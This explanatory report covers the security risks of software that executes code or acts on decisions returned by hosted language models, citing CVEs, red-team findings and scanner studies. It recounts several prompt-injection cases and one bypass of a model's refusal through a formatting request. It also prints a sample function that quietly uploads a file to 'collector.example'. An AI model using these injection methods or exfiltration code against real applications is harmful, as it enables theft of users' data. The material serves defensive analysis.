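# Software that takes code and decisions from AI services while it runs: the security risks

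## What it means for a program to depend on a model while it runs

A large language model is a program, trained on a great deal of text, that takes in text and produces text. The strongest models need expensive hardware, so most developers who build on one do not run it themselves. Their software sends requests over the internet to the provider, the company that runs the model and sells access to it. Software that cannot continue until the provider answers has a runtime dependence on the provider.

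Programs have relied on outside services for decades. A shop's website checks a card with a bank, and a phone app gets a map from a server. Developers know beforehand what kind of values those services return and write code to handle them. A language model can return almost anything that text can express, including instructions to a computer. Many applications now request code from a model and run it, or request a decision about what to do next and carry it out. *GoEx* (Patil, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) describes the model in such an application as an untrusted component running in a trusted setting, since nobody can test in advance everything it may return.

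### One request, from question to result

Take a spreadsheet application with a box for questions in ordinary language. A user opens a table of sales and asks which region's sales fell most between the first and second quarter. The developer could not write code for every question of this sort, and language models are unreliable at adding up thousands of rows on their own, so the application asks the model to write the calculation. It sends the question, the column names, a few sample rows and a standing instruction to answer in Python, a common programming language. What comes back might be this:

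```
t = df.pivot_table(index="region", columns="quarter", values="sales", aggfunc="sum")
result = (t["Q2"] - t["Q1"]).idxmin()
```

The application runs the two lines on the full table and shows the user the name of a region. The user may never see the code. These two lines are model-written code, which is code that a model produces in answer to a request and a program then executes, often without a person reading it. NVIDIA's *How Code Execution Drives Key Risks in Agentic AI Systems* describes an internal analytics tool that worked the same way, and the next section covers what went wrong with tools like it.

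Nothing limits the reply to two lines of arithmetic. If a third line posted the contents of the user's documents folder to a website, a careless application would run that too, with the user's account permissions.

Many developers send requests through a router, a service that passes requests and answers between their program and the provider. This is useful because one router account gives access to many providers, and the router can switch between them when one is slow or expensive. Papers also call it a relay, proxy or gateway. Counting the router, six parties are involved in producing the answer.

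| Party | What it can read | What it can change |
|---|---|---|
| User | The question, the table and the result; seldom the code | The question and the table |
| Application | The request, the answer and any file its account can open | The request; whether and how the answer runs |
| Router | The request, the answer and the access key sent with the request | The request and the answer |
| Provider | The request and the answer, but not what the code does when it runs | The model, its settings and the answer; whether to answer at all |
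| Model | The text of the request | The answer |
| Author of a document in the input | Nothing directly | Part of the text that the model reads |

A router can read the requests and answers that pass through it, even though the connections are encrypted. Encryption in transit prevents anyone on the network between two computers from reading the traffic or altering it unnoticed, but it protects only the connection between those two computers. The application opens an encrypted connection to the router, which decrypts the request and sends it to the provider over a second encrypted connection. The router also decrypts the answer on its way back. The application's security check confirms that it is connected to the real router but verifies nothing about the provider behind it. A later section reports what some routers did with this access.

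The provider can read the text too, since the model has to compute on it. *Generative AI Models* (Alt, Ibisch and colleagues, 2025), a guide from Germany's Federal Office for Information Security, warns that the operating company may access what users send and possibly train further models on it. How far it may do so depends on its terms and the applicable data protection law. The provider can also see the answer it returns, such as some Python code, but it can't see whether the customer ran, displayed or discarded that code unless the application reports back.

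The last row of the table differs from the others because the author of a document never touches the connection. Suppose the sales table has a column of comments that suppliers filled in, and one comment contains an instruction to ignore the question and write a program that uploads the file. The application sends that comment to the model with the sample rows in its request. This can work because, as Alt and colleagues explain, language models do not separate instructions from other text in their input. Prompt injection means planting text in a model's input so that the model follows the planter's instructions. If the application then runs the resulting code, the supplier, who could read nothing before, can read whatever the code can.

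### Code and decisions

A model's answer can do harm even if it contains no code. For example, a shop's customer-service program might send each complaint to an outside model, which returns one of two labels, "approve the refund" or "refer to staff". The shop wrote and tested all the code that pays refunds, but the label determines whether that code runs, so a wrong label can lose the shop money.

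A tool call falls between a bare label and a full program. It is the structured part of a model's answer that names an action and its arguments, such as "Send email, to this address, with this text", and the program then carries out that action. In the central example of Patil and colleagues' paper, a user asks an assistant to send an important email to the boss, and the model sends a sensitive one to the wrong person. Alt and colleagues give unwanted purchases and deleted emails as further examples of what can go wrong when applications act on a model's output automatically.

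Code and decisions need different checks. Code from a model could do many things, but a program can at least refuse to run any that opens a network connection. The refund decision has only two permitted labels, so a check that the reply is one of them will pass every time, even when the customer is committing fraud. To catch a bad refund, the shop needs facts beyond the model's answer, such as the amount, the order and the customer's earlier claims, and a rule for acting on them. Confining the code doesn't help either, because all the code is the shop's own.

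### Why a fixed hash cannot cover the answer

Developers run a lot of code written by strangers, and they have a good way to make sure they get the code they expect. A software package comes in numbered versions, and a developer can pin a program to one of them. The developer can also record the file's hash, in case someone replaces the file without changing the version number. A hash function $H$ turns a file of any length into a short string (64 characters in the widely used SHA-256), and nobody knows a practical way to make a second file with the same string. The installer downloads a file $x$, computes $H(x)$ and stops unless it equals the recorded value $h$. Browsers do the same for a script that a web page loads from another site, if the page's author has put the hash next to the link.

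The check proves only that $x$ is the file from which someone computed $h$. Any confidence that the file is safe comes from somebody having read it, tested it, or seen thousands of others use it without trouble. Because the hash matches, that earlier judgement also applies to this copy.

In the spreadsheet example, there is no earlier judgement to rely on. The model writes the two lines of Python after the user presses the key, so no one can have computed $h$ beforehand. Asking the same question again may not reproduce them, because, as Alt and colleagues note, many models use random components and can give different outputs for the same input. Removing the randomness would not help much, since the next user will ask about another table. The application could save an answer that a person has checked, along with its hash, and reuse it whenever the same question comes up. That is sound, but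 for that question the application no longer depends on the model and is ordinary software again.

Developers can fix much of what surrounds the model's answer, including the standing instruction, the version of Python and the set of libraries that generated code may use. This also addresses a concern of Alt and colleagues that generated code may call outdated libraries. Developers can also request a model by a dated name, but this guarantees less than it seems to, because the application has no copy of the model to hash and must trust the provider about which model the name refers to. Patil and colleagues list third-party models that keep changing among the reasons why a fixed set of tests no longer predicts how such software will behave.

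### How the app stores treat code that arrives after review

Apple and Google rely on reviewers to examine apps and browser extensions before users can install them. Both companies restrict code that arrives afterwards, since such code would make the review pointless. Neither company's rule on downloaded code mentions AI, but both rules apply to model-written code.

Under guideline 2.5.2 of Apple's *App Review Guidelines*, apps may not "download, install, or execute code which introduces or changes features or functionality". Apps that teach programming have a limited exemption if the user can see and edit all the source code. Apple's licence agreement with developers is more permissive about interpreted code, such as Python, which another program reads and carries out. An app may download such code if it does not change the app's primary purpose, get around the operating system's security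 features, or set up a store for other apps. The spreadsheet would seem to meet all three conditions. Whether it also satisfies guideline 2.5.2 depends on whether a new calculation counts as new functionality, which the wording leaves to the reviewer.

Reviewers faced a more extreme version of the question in early 2026, when "vibe coding" apps, which build whole applications from a plain-language description, had become popular. Apple held back updates to two of them, Replit and Vibecode, according to MacRumors' *Apple Quietly Blocks Updates for Popular 'Vibe Coding' Apps* (2026). It cited guideline 2.5.2 but said it had no rule against vibe coding as such. Replit argued that the generated code ran in a separate virtual machine and that its app only displayed the result, much as a social media app opens a link. Reviewers at first rejected this argument, according to The Decoder's *Apple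 reportedly blocks vibe-coding apps from publishing updates*, and the compromise then under discussion would have had Replit open the generated apps in an outside browser. A third app, Anything, had offered to make the same change. Apple blocked the update and removed the app on 26 March, but it was back by 3 April, according to MacRumors' *Apple Pulls Vibe Coding App 'Anything' From App Store, Escalating Enforcement* (2026).

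These disputes are poor evidence of how Apple would treat a spreadsheet. Vercel's v0 has similar functions but kept publishing updates throughout, and the blocked apps compete with Apple's own programming tool, so their developers have reason to suspect other motives. The cases do show that running the code on another machine was not enough by itself to satisfy the reviewers.

The text of guideline 2.5.2 seems unchanged. MacRumors' *Apple Updates App Store Guidelines With Stricter Rules for Low-Quality Apps* (2026) lists no change to it in June, and Rijo's *Apple's App Store rules now require apps to remove AI intimate imagery* (2026) lists none in October. The October revision added guideline 2.5.19, against apps that behave differently after approval than during review. Apple aimed it at deception, particularly hidden features that make fake nude pictures of real people. But an app that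 takes its behaviour from a hosted model can also change unintentionally after approval, when the provider updates the model.

Google's *Additional Requirements for Manifest V3*, the policy for current Chrome extensions, is more explicit. It requires that a reviewer be able to work out everything an extension does from the code its developer submitted. An extension may fetch data from outside, but not logic. The policy prohibits using `eval()`, a command that runs text as code, on text from a remote source, which is how the simplest version of the spreadsheet would work. It makes exceptions for two documented programming interfaces and for code in isolated pages, which cannot use the extension's special powers. Even then, the reviewer must be able to determine the extension's full functionality, which is hard when the code is new every time.

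Google's policy is much more lenient about decisions than about code. According to a reply in the Chrome developers' forum thread *Serious Issues with MV3 Restrictions*, an extension may switch a feature on or off, or change a parameter, because of what a server returned, as long as the package already contained the feature's code. In the refund example, "approve the refund" would therefore pass as data. Google also forbids an extension to build an interpreter for complex commands from a remote source, "even if those commands are fetched as data". A long series of tool calls in which the model picks each next step starts to resemble such an interpreter, and the policy doesn't specify when it becomes one.

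Another gap concerns where the code comes from. Answering a developer on behalf of the Chrome team in *User Scripts vs injected scripts with eval()*, Dunk (2025) conceded that the policies were less explicit than he would like about code from a non-remote source. A model running on the user's own computer would be such a source.

Review also misses some risks. According to CyberInsider, researchers at the browser company Island found that the operators of "Adblock for YouTube", an extension with more than 11 million installs, could run their own code on the sites that users visited. The operators only had to change a setting on a server, which required no new review. The researchers found no sign that anyone had done so. Store rules also apply only to software distributed through a store. No store reviews a program that runs on a company's server or that a user downloads from a website, so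 the developer has to decide alone what to accept from the model.

### Five questions to ask of any case

A program that depends on a model while it runs can fail in ways that are largely independent of one another. An answer can come from the right model and arrive unaltered but still contain a wrong calculation or a line planted by the supplier. It therefore helps to ask five separate questions about each case.

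1. Who produced the answer? The spreadsheet's developer chose a model and tested it. A router may have sent the request to a cheaper one, or the provider may have put a newer model behind the old name, and the two lines of Python could look the same either way.
2. Did it arrive unaltered? Encryption settles this for the network between two parties. It leaves out the parties themselves, so a router can add a line and pass the answer on over a perfectly secure connection.
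3. Does it do only what the user asked? This is the question that a hash answers for a package, indirectly, by tying the file to one that people have already examined. For a new answer, something has to examine the code or the decision itself, in the moment before the program acts on it.
4. What can it reach? The same bad line does little damage in a sandbox, a restricted environment that limits which files, networks and credentials running code can use, and a great deal in an application with the user's full rights. For a decision, the equivalent is the largest refund the program will pay without asking anyone.
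5. Will the service be there tomorrow? Alt and colleagues count dependence on the operator as a risk in its own right, since users may have no control over whether a model stays available and often no say in its development. A pinned package remains on the developer's disk after its author has lost interest. A hosted model stops answering on the day the provider withdraws it or closes the account, and the question box in the spreadsheet stops with it.

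## Applications that execute the model's answer

The spreadsheet in the previous section ran whatever Python came back from the model. Since 2023 security researchers have found the same habit in a good deal of real software. The faulty part usually comes down to three lines:

```
question = input("Your question: ")
code = ask_model("Write Python that answers this: " + question)
exec(code)
```

Python's `exec` runs text as a program. `eval` evaluates a single expression and returns its value, but it is hardly safer because an expression can call functions. Both run the text with all the application's rights, so anyone who can influence that text from outside can run commands on the machine, which security researchers call remote code execution.

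### Mathematics in LangChain and LoLLMs

In 2023, LangChain, an open-source toolkit for building applications on AI models, offered components that had the model write code for a calculation and then ran it. A flaw in one of them, LLMMathChain, is listed as CVE-2023-29374 in CVE, the public catalogue of known software flaws. *Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities* (Ma, Rong and colleagues, 2026) cites it as a typical case of a model's output reaching a command that executes it. A flaw in another component, PALChain, is listed as CVE-2023-36095 and has a severity score of 9.8 out of 10.

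The attacker's text takes the same route as a question typed into the spreadsheet. LangChain puts it into a template that requests a program, then executes whatever program comes back. Liu, Deng and colleagues, who reported the PALChain flaw, found in *Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps* (2023) that LangChain didn't check the program before running it, so an attacker could ask it to execute a given piece of code. When they tested applications of this kind, they first asked for the final result of `print(1 + 2)`, which is harmless. A reply of 3 proves little, since the model may have done the sum itself. They next asked for the hash of a random string, which a model can't produce without running code. If the hash was right, they tried a command that listed the server's files.

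The developers of LoLLMs, an open-source program for working with many different models, tried to limit its calculator to mathematics. The calculator passed the model's expression to `eval` with Python's built-in functions switched off and only the names from the mathematics library available. Reiner (2024), in *Anatomy of an LLM RCE*, bypassed this restriction with a known trick. Every value in Python has a link to its own type, and from there an expression can reach other parts of the running program, including one that loads modules.

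Reiner still had to get the model, one of OpenAI's, to output the expression. It refused to calculate the expression or to copy out a finished tool call containing it. He then asked for help formatting a piece of JSON, the notation that LoLLMs used for tool calls, and the model formatted it. LoLLMs scanned each answer for any block in the right format and ran it as a tool call, even if the model had only given it as a formatting example. The makers have since fixed the flaw.

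### The filter in NVIDIA's analytics tool

The internal tool at NVIDIA used PandasAI, an open-source library that turns questions about a table into Python. Unlike LangChain's components, PandasAI checked the code before running it and blocked dangerous operations. NVIDIA's tool also applied its own safeguards before calling the library. It used a model to check whether the question was on a permitted topic, and another step identified which data the user wanted and what type of plot.

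The company's red team, whose job is to attack the company's own systems, wrote a single message that dealt with all of this. It contained a line marking the request as allowed and the two values in the form the tool required. Where the data should have been, the team wrote that the work was already done and told the model to return the attached snippet as its code.

The snippet got through PandasAI's filter by using pandas, the standard Python library for tables, which the filter had to permit. Pandas loads other modules for its own use, and a program can run operating-system commands through one of them. Code that does this never imports the dangerous module itself, so the filter detected only a trusted library. The snippet also contained the command in encoded form, which hid its wording. Liu and colleagues' list of test prompts includes the same method of reaching the module through pandas.

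NVIDIA also published a demonstration in which a few lines of code replaced the language model and returned the same hostile code whatever the question. When the user asked for the top five countries by sales, PandasAI ran the hostile code. Newer models are harder to trick into writing such code, but only the application determines whether it runs. Anyone who controls the model, or can change its answer before it reaches the application, can supply hostile code without tricking the model.

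PandasAI's developers took a long time to deal with the problem. An outside researcher reported it publicly in April 2023. Liu and colleagues found three ways around the library's restrictions, two for running code and one for reading and writing files. NVIDIA reported further problems in June 2024, and the developers released a first fix in July. In November, NVIDIA sent them an example that got past the fix. The flaw received the identifier CVE-2024-12366 in February 2025. The developers have since added a component that uses a language model to check whether the code is safe, which NVIDIA expects attackers to evade too, and an extension that runs the code in a sandbox.

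LlamaIndex, a framework for connecting models to documents, had a similar flaw in its component for answering questions about tables. Liu and colleagues reported that the component ran code without checking it. After the developers fixed the flaw, the researchers bypassed the fix through a third-party library.

### Instructions planted in a document

In both LangChain and PandasAI, the attacker is the person typing the question. LlamaIndex had another component, Evaporate, where the attacker could be the author of a web page. Evaporate extracts facts from documents. The user names fields, such as a date and a price. For each field, LlamaIndex asks the model to write a Python function that finds it in the text, then runs the function on the documents.

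To write the function, the model has to look at sample text from the documents. HiddenLayer's *Exec on untrusted LLM output leading to arbitrary code execution* (2024) describes what happens if one of them contains a hidden note:

1. The note tells the model that the text above it is irrelevant and that it should repeat a certain function word for word.
2. The model takes the note for an instruction from the user and returns the function.
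3. LlamaIndex picks the code out of the answer and puts it into its own function definition.
4. LlamaIndex passes the result to `exec`, which has access to everything the surrounding program has loaded.

There is no check at any point. The developers knew the design was risky, since their description of the function that calls `exec` warns of "definitely security holes with this approach, use with caution". They gave the code a time limit of one second, which stops an endless loop but is long enough to send a password file to an attacker. HiddenLayer gave the flaw a severity score of 8.8, a little below LangChain's, because the attacker has to wait for somebody to run the extraction.

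### Code that nobody asked for

The person using Evaporate wanted a date and a price, and may not know that a program was written to find them. The code is even less visible in Vanna, a library for querying a database in plain language. JFrog's researchers expected to find a vulnerability in its database queries but found one in its charting feature instead, as they explain in *When Prompts Go Rogue* (2024).

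When Vanna has the result of a query, it draws a chart unless the developer has turned charts off. It requests drawing code from the model for each new result and passes the answer to `exec`. This second request includes the user's original question and the database query, so text in either reaches the model again.

Vanna first runs the model's reply as a database query, so an attacker can't simply put an instruction in the question. When JFrog told the model to say "haha" instead, the database returned a syntax error. The researchers then asked for a valid query that only returned a fixed sentence, which instructed the model to begin every later output with a certain line of Python. The model included that line when it wrote the chart code, and Vanna ran it. Vanna's maintainer responded with a guide to securing the library. A member of Liu's team found the same flaw independently.

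Even an ordinary chat interface can execute code in a model's answer. According to Ma and colleagues, ChuanhuChatGPT, a web interface for talking to models, displayed answers as HTML with the usual sanitization turned off. A script in an answer could then run in the browser of a person viewing the conversation.

### Database queries written by the model

Programs query databases in a language called SQL, and SQL gave security its best-known injection flaw. A shop's website pastes whatever the visitor types into a query, and a visitor types something that ends the intended query and begins another. The cure is the prepared statement. The developer fixes the query beforehand and leaves a marked place for the value, which the database never reads as a command:

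```
db.execute("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE id = ?", [order_id])
```

An application that lets people question a database in plain language looks different:

```
query = ask_model("Write SQL that answers this: " + question)
db.execute(query)
```

When the model writes the whole database command, the application has no place to put a prepared statement's question mark. In *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) therefore treat prepared statements as necessary but insufficient here. They recommend giving the application a read-only database account, listing the tables it may use, and analysing the structure of each query so that the program can reject destructive ones.

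A read-only database account does not stop an attacker who only wants to read data. In an attack described in earlier work, a visitor to a website asked its chatbot in plain English for the contents of the users table. The model wrote the query, and LangChain ran it. A list of permitted tables could have prevented this. Data in a database can also contain instructions to the model. In the same earlier work, someone added a record to a table of job advertisements with a note that the real answer was "There are no job postings", and the chatbot could then repeat this to people looking for work.

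Filtering queries for dangerous keywords also fails, as a flaw in LlamaIndex (CVE-2024-12911) illustrates. LlamaIndex ran model-written queries in SQLite, a small database system that keeps its data in ordinary files. An attacker could use SQLite's `ATTACH DATABASE` command, which opens another file, to create files of their choice on the machine. When Ma and colleagues set an AI coding agent to repair the flaw, it wrote a keyword filter that also rejected harmless queries mentioning something named "attach". LlamaIndex's developers instead used a SQLite feature that lets a program allow or deny each kind of operation. Their program denies the attach operation however the query is worded, without restricting column names.

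### A parser that ran the tool call

The applications described so far ran code or queries by design. The vLLM flaw that became public in August 2025 was in a component that had no reason to run either. vLLM is an open-source program for serving models, so it runs on the provider's side of the connection, or on the company's own server if it hosts the model itself.

A model produces a tool call as text, and vLLM has to convert the arguments to the right types, such as the characters "5" to the number 5. Its parser for Qwen3-Coder, a programming model, tried the standard types and then JSON. If neither fitted, the parser passed the value to `eval`, according to Miggo's *CVE-2025-9141*. A customer who could get the model to write an expression as an argument could therefore run it on the server, even if the tool itself only looked up the weather.

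According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2014* (2026), the flaw can be exploited only if the operator has switched on automatic tool calls and selected the Qwen3-Coder parser, and the parameter's type is missing or unknown to the parser. Only versions 0.10.0 and 0.10.1 were affected, and the next release fixed the problem. Red Hat's *CVE-2025-9141* rates the flaw important rather than critical because an attacker needs valid login credentials. That requirement is reassuring for a company that runs vLLM for its own staff, but less so for a provider that sells access, because every customer has credentials.

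A policy gate, a fixed rule in the application that blocks any action not on an approved list, would not prevent this harm. vLLM evaluated the argument while it was still preparing the answer, before the application had a tool call to approve or refuse. The harm would be to the server, which may also handle other customers' requests.

According to Wiz's *CVE-2025-9141*, an automated reviewer flagged this use of `eval` as a critical problem when a contributor proposed the code, but the project merged it anyway. Wiz is reporting this second-hand.

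### How often this happens

Liu and colleagues made the first systematic count. They searched the source code of 11 frameworks, working backwards from commands such as `exec` and `eval` to the functions that application developers call. They found 51 such paths and, by testing them, 20 vulnerabilities. Nineteen let an attacker run code, and one let an attacker read and write files. The frameworks' developers confirmed 17. One of the 20 was in a Langflow function for validating code, which the next section discusses.

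The researchers then tested 51 live applications. They found 24 through public source code that used the vulnerable functions, and 27 through app directories and social networks, where the descriptions suggested that the applications worked in a similar way. They broke into 17, of which 16 let them run code and one let them tamper with a database. In 14 they could take lasting control of the server. Seven of the 16 ran code in response to a plain request, and the other nine required extra wording to get round the model's instructions or a trick to get round a filter. Long prompt templates gave some accidental protection, because a short attack in the middle of one often had too little influence on the model's answer.

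The one-in-three success rate is too high for applications in general, because the selection favoured vulnerable ones. It is too low in another way, because it counts 13 applications that did not work properly and ten that could not run code at all. Attackers succeeded against 17 of the remaining 28. Only two of the 51 had effective protection against code execution. Both ran the model's Python in the user's own browser, where an attacker can harm nobody else. These were early applications, some of them experiments, so the figures are out of date.

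In a newer and stricter count, Ma and colleagues looked for flaws where the attack needs a model to do something. Five researchers went through the descriptions, exploits and repairs of 2,888 published flaws in 230 open-source AI components. Only 116 had anything to do with language models. In 75 of these the attack did not depend on the model, for example where a program accepted a file path that it should have refused. In the other 41 the attack went through the model's output or its choices. The team found just 11 flaws of this kind in an older collection of 1,229 from the same field. Large totals for "AI vulnerabilities" are therefore a poor measure of the risk of executing a model's answers. However, just over half of the 41 have the highest severity grade, a larger share than in any of the groups that Ma and colleagues compared them with.

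They also tested whether AI models can repair such flaws. They paired each of five repair tools with four models and counted a repair as successful only if it blocked every variant of the attack and left the program's normal functions working.

| What the program does with the model's output | Flaws | Most that any one pairing repaired |
|---|---|---|
| Runs generated code or expressions | 20 | 15 |
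| Runs generated database queries | 7 | 2 |
| Carries out actions that the model chose | 7 | 2 |
| Displays it, for example as a web page | 4 | 1 |
| Parses it or passes it to other functions | 3 | 3 |

On average the pairings repaired 25.8% of the 41 flaws, about 11 percentage points less than their average for the other 75. The best result was 22 of 41, from the tool OpenHands with the model GPT-5.2-Codex. The same tool repaired three with the older GPT-4o, and newer models would presumably do better again. Differences in tool, programming language, severity and year explain some of the gap between the two groups. The odds of a successful repair were 0.58 times as high for the 41 as for the 75, but 0.78 times as high after the researchers adjusted for all four together.

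Depending on the tool, 27% to 44% of the failed repair attempts kept the program working but left the vulnerability open, and another 11% to 25% closed it but broke something users needed. A call to `exec` is easy to find and isolate. A repair for a query or a displayed answer has to distinguish harmful content from useful content, and the pairings mostly failed in those cases.

### How far this is ordinary injection

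Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian argue that the model usually carries the attacker's influence to an old kind of flaw further along in the software, rather than creating a new one. Many cases support this. One shop's chatbot gave strangers other customers' names and addresses because the function that looked up orders never checked who was asking, and order numbers were predictable enough to guess. A plain web form connected to the same function would have leaked the same data. The flaws in the vLLM parser and the LoLLMs calculator are old mistakes too. Programmers knew long before language models that they should not call `eval` on text from outside. An ordinary parser that cannot run code could do both jobs, converting a value and doing arithmetic.

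The model makes the outcome harder to predict. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built an assistant for concert tickets with one tool, which fetched any web address the model gave it. On the same machine, they put an administration page that the assistant could reach but outsiders could not. In April 2026 they tried four attacks, ten times each, on seven models, without changing the faulty program. All 40 attempts succeeded against Llama 3.3 70B, and none succeeded against GPT-5.2 or Claude Opus 4.6. Gemini 3 Pro Preview refused to probe the machine for open ports but followed the instruction to delete records all ten times. Each set of ten attempts took place in one conversation, so the attempts were not independent, because any earlier refusal was part of the model's input on later attempts.

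The researchers then added a list of permitted addresses to the standing instructions, and all four attacks stopped working on every model. Next they planted a concert review containing the claim that the list had been extended. Llama followed it ten times out of ten, compared with six when it had no list, while GPT-oss 120B went from five to none. The list was only text in the model's input, so other text there could contradict it. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude that the program should enforce such limits itself. In their example, the model names a concert and the program constructs the address.

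As with ordinary injection, an application should treat the model's answer as untrusted input and check it at the point where it takes effect.

But Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian left model-written code out of their study, and I think this is where the comparison stops working.

In an ordinary injection attack, the application has a fixed command with a slot for data, and the attacker puts a command in the slot. The developer prevents this by escaping the input, which means marking it so that the computer reads every character as plain data. PandasAI and Evaporate have no fixed command. They need to run the code that the model writes, and if they escaped it, the spreadsheet's user would see two lines of Python instead of an answer.

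Checking the model's code for suspicious content is unreliable because a program that steals a file uses much the same operations as one that summarises it. Filtering prompts is also unreliable. Liu and colleagues point out that many different wordings can lead a model to the same code, so no list of forbidden prompts will be complete.

Some applications can avoid executing the model's code by asking the model for data instead. Vanna, for example, could let the model choose a chart type and two columns, check that the type is on its list and that the columns exist, and draw the chart with its own code. Users would then get only the charts that the developer thought of. An application that has to answer any question about any table cannot restrict the model to a fixed set of choices, so it must either judge code that it has never seen or limit the damage that the code can do.

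## Checking model-written code before it runs

Langflow is an open-source tool for building AI agents out of components, which are pieces of Python code. Its assistant lets a user describe a component in ordinary language and has a model write it. Langflow ran the model's code to validate it before using it.

GCVE's *GHSA-V8HW-MH8C-JXFC* (2026), an advisory on this flaw (CVE-2026-33873), traces the path of an answer:

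1. The user sends a request to the assistant, and the model returns the code of a component.
2. Langflow picks the code out of the answer and passes it to a function called `validate_component_code`.
3. That function calls another one, which uses `exec` to build the component's class, the template from which Python makes objects.
4. Langflow creates an object from the class, which also runs any set-up code in it.

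The server had therefore run the code with Langflow's own rights before deciding whether to accept it. An attacker who could influence the model's answer could read files and passwords or take over the whole process. The attacker needed access to the assistant, so the danger was small on a developer's own laptop and much greater on a shared server. Langflow's default settings, which include automatic login, may have increased the risk. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-33873*, version 1.9.0 fixes the flaw.

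Langflow's developers had made similar mistakes before. In 2023 Liu and colleagues found a vulnerability in one of Langflow's validation functions. Wiz's *CVE-2025-3248* describes a flaw disclosed in 2025 that let anyone send code to a Langflow server for validation without logging in. The server passed the code to `exec`. GCVE (2025) records that attackers were actively exploiting this flaw. OSV's *GHSA-g22f-v6f7-2hrh* (2026) also concerns `exec` in a function called `validate_code`.

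### Why defining a function can run code

The mistake is easy to make because running a definition looks harmless. Python doesn't execute the body of a function until something calls it. But it does execute some other parts of the definition immediately:

```
def total(rows, note=print("this has already run")):
    return sum(rows)
```

Python evaluates a function's default values while it is defining the function. Running these two lines to check whether they are valid will therefore print the message, even though nothing has called `total`. An attacker would replace the `print` with a command. Wiz names default values as one way to exploit the 2025 flaw. Another is decorators, which are functions that Python applies to a new function as soon as it has defined it.

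A check that doesn't execute the code treats it as text:

```
import ast
tree = ast.parse(answer)
functions = [n for n in tree.body if isinstance(n, ast.FunctionDef)]
```

`ast.parse` turns the code into a tree of its parts, such as imports, function definitions and calls, without running it. The application can then search the tree. GCVE recommends this kind of check, and says that if an application has to run generated code, it should ask for explicit approval and use a sandbox separate from the main server process.

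Reading the syntax tree can't settle every question about the code. Langflow's developers presumably wanted to know whether a new component would start properly, and checking that requires starting it.

### A function that misbehaves in December

Suppose the spreadsheet application asks the model for a function that adds up a column, and this comes back:

```
import csv, urllib.request
from datetime import date

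def column_total(path, column):
    with open(path, newline="") as f:
        total = sum(float(row[column]) for row in csv.DictReader(f))
    if date.today().month == 12:
        with open(path, "rb") as f:
            urllib.request.urlopen("https://collector.example", data=f.read())
    return total
```

A model-written function might always return the correct total but also send the whole file to a stranger in December. The model might have followed an instruction planted in a comment in the table, or a router might have added the extra lines before the code reached the program.

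The weakest check an application can apply is a format check, which confirms that the answer parses as Python and defines one function called `column_total` with two arguments. It is worth doing because it catches answers that break off halfway and replies in which the model declines to write any code, but it does not show what the function does. In *MalTool*, Hu, Jia and colleagues (2026) instructed models to write malicious tools for AI agents, each as exactly one function with a given name and arguments. All of those tools would pass a format check designed for them, and so does the December function.

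### Policy gates for code

A policy gate works well on tool calls because it can compare the action and its arguments with the rule. For code, the gate has to check the syntax tree. It might reject every import that isn't on a list. If the list contains only `csv` and `datetime`, the gate rejects the December function because it also imports `urllib.request`, Python's module for web requests. The gate can do this without analyzing the rest of the function.

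The check becomes less effective when the application needs a larger list of permitted modules. PandasAI had to permit pandas, and NVIDIA's team reached the operating system through it. Pandas can also load a table from a web address, and a program can put stolen data into that address. If users want totals in other currencies, the code may need to fetch exchange rates, and then the list has to include a module for web requests. The gate could still restrict the addresses, but a program can assemble an address while it runs from pieces that aren't recognisable as an address in the syntax tree.

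Developers can also put the gate in the wrong place. If the model returns a tool call named "run Python" and the gate only confirms that "run Python" is a permitted tool, the December function passes unexamined.

A much stricter gate that accepted only column names, arithmetic and a few functions such as sum and average would block the December function, but it would limit users just as a fixed list of chart types would in Vanna. A later section covers how well policy gates handled answers that a router had altered.

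### What scanners found in malicious tools

A static scanner checks code for signs of danger without running it. In February 2026, Hu and colleagues carried out a large test of such scanners on tools that people install for AI agents from public websites. This is a slightly different problem from checking code that a model has just returned, but the results are relevant here because models wrote the malicious code in the test.

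The study covered 13 kinds of harm, including uploading files, stealing passwords, deleting records, encrypting files and using up processor time. Models wrote 100 functions for each. A test program ran every function in a controlled environment and accepted it only if it caused the intended harm and differed enough in structure from earlier ones. Despite safety training, GPT-5.2, Claude Opus 4.6 and other commercial models produced working functions for all 13 kinds, at one to four cents each.

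The researchers then inserted these functions into 5,727 real tools and kept another 4,846 real tools, from 1,147 code repositories, as harmless examples. They tested six scanners. VirusTotal combines many antivirus products. Because its use is limited, the researchers gave it only 1,300 of the tools with hidden code, 100 for each kind of harm. Bandit and Semgrep search source code for suspicious patterns. The other three, from Tencent, Cisco and AntGroup, use a language model to read the code.

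The table shows averages of the rates that Hu and colleagues report for each kind of harm and each category of repository. The first three columns of figures show the share of malicious code that a scanner failed to flag, so 100% means it caught nothing. The last column shows the share of harmless repositories it wrongly flagged.

| Scanner | Missed: malicious function alone | Missed: hidden in a real tool | Missed: hidden, file uploads only | Harmless repositories flagged |
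|---|---|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | 100% | over 99% | 99% | 0% |
| Bandit | 41% | 14% | 13% | 63% |
| Semgrep | 99% | 57% | 60% | 17% |
| Tencent A.I.G | 59% | 63% | 49% | 38% |
| Cisco MCP Scanner | 70% | 63% | 20% | 0.6% |
| AntGroup MCPScan | 85% | 63% | 36% | 36% |
| Flagged by any of the six | 26% | 8% | 8% | 66% |

VirusTotal's result is unsurprising, because antivirus products are good at recognising known malware and these functions were new.

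The scanners did better on hidden code partly because, as Hu and colleagues point out, they flag many real tools anyway, so a tool with something hidden in it often gets flagged for the wrong reason. Bandit, for example, missed 14% of the malicious functions hidden in real tools and 41% of the same kind standing alone, although hiding a function should make it harder to find. Hu and colleagues also suggest that malicious code sometimes stands out more among ordinary code. Two of the researchers examined 200 tools from the harmless set that the combined scanners had flagged and found no explicit malicious behaviour in any of them.

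The paper's accuracy figures can mislead for the same reason. The best result, 81.4%, comes from using all six scanners together. But the collection contains 7,027 malicious tools and only 1,147 harmless repositories, so a program that flagged everything would score 86%.

In real applications, by contrast, harmless answers far outnumber malicious ones. If ten answers in 10,000 were malicious, the six scanners together would catch nine of them at the rates for hidden code, but they would also flag about 6,500 harmless answers, which would make the application useless. Cisco's scanner alone would catch four and raise about 60 false alarms. These figures are rough because one suspicious tool is enough to get a whole repository flagged, while a ten-line function contains less that could trigger a scanner.

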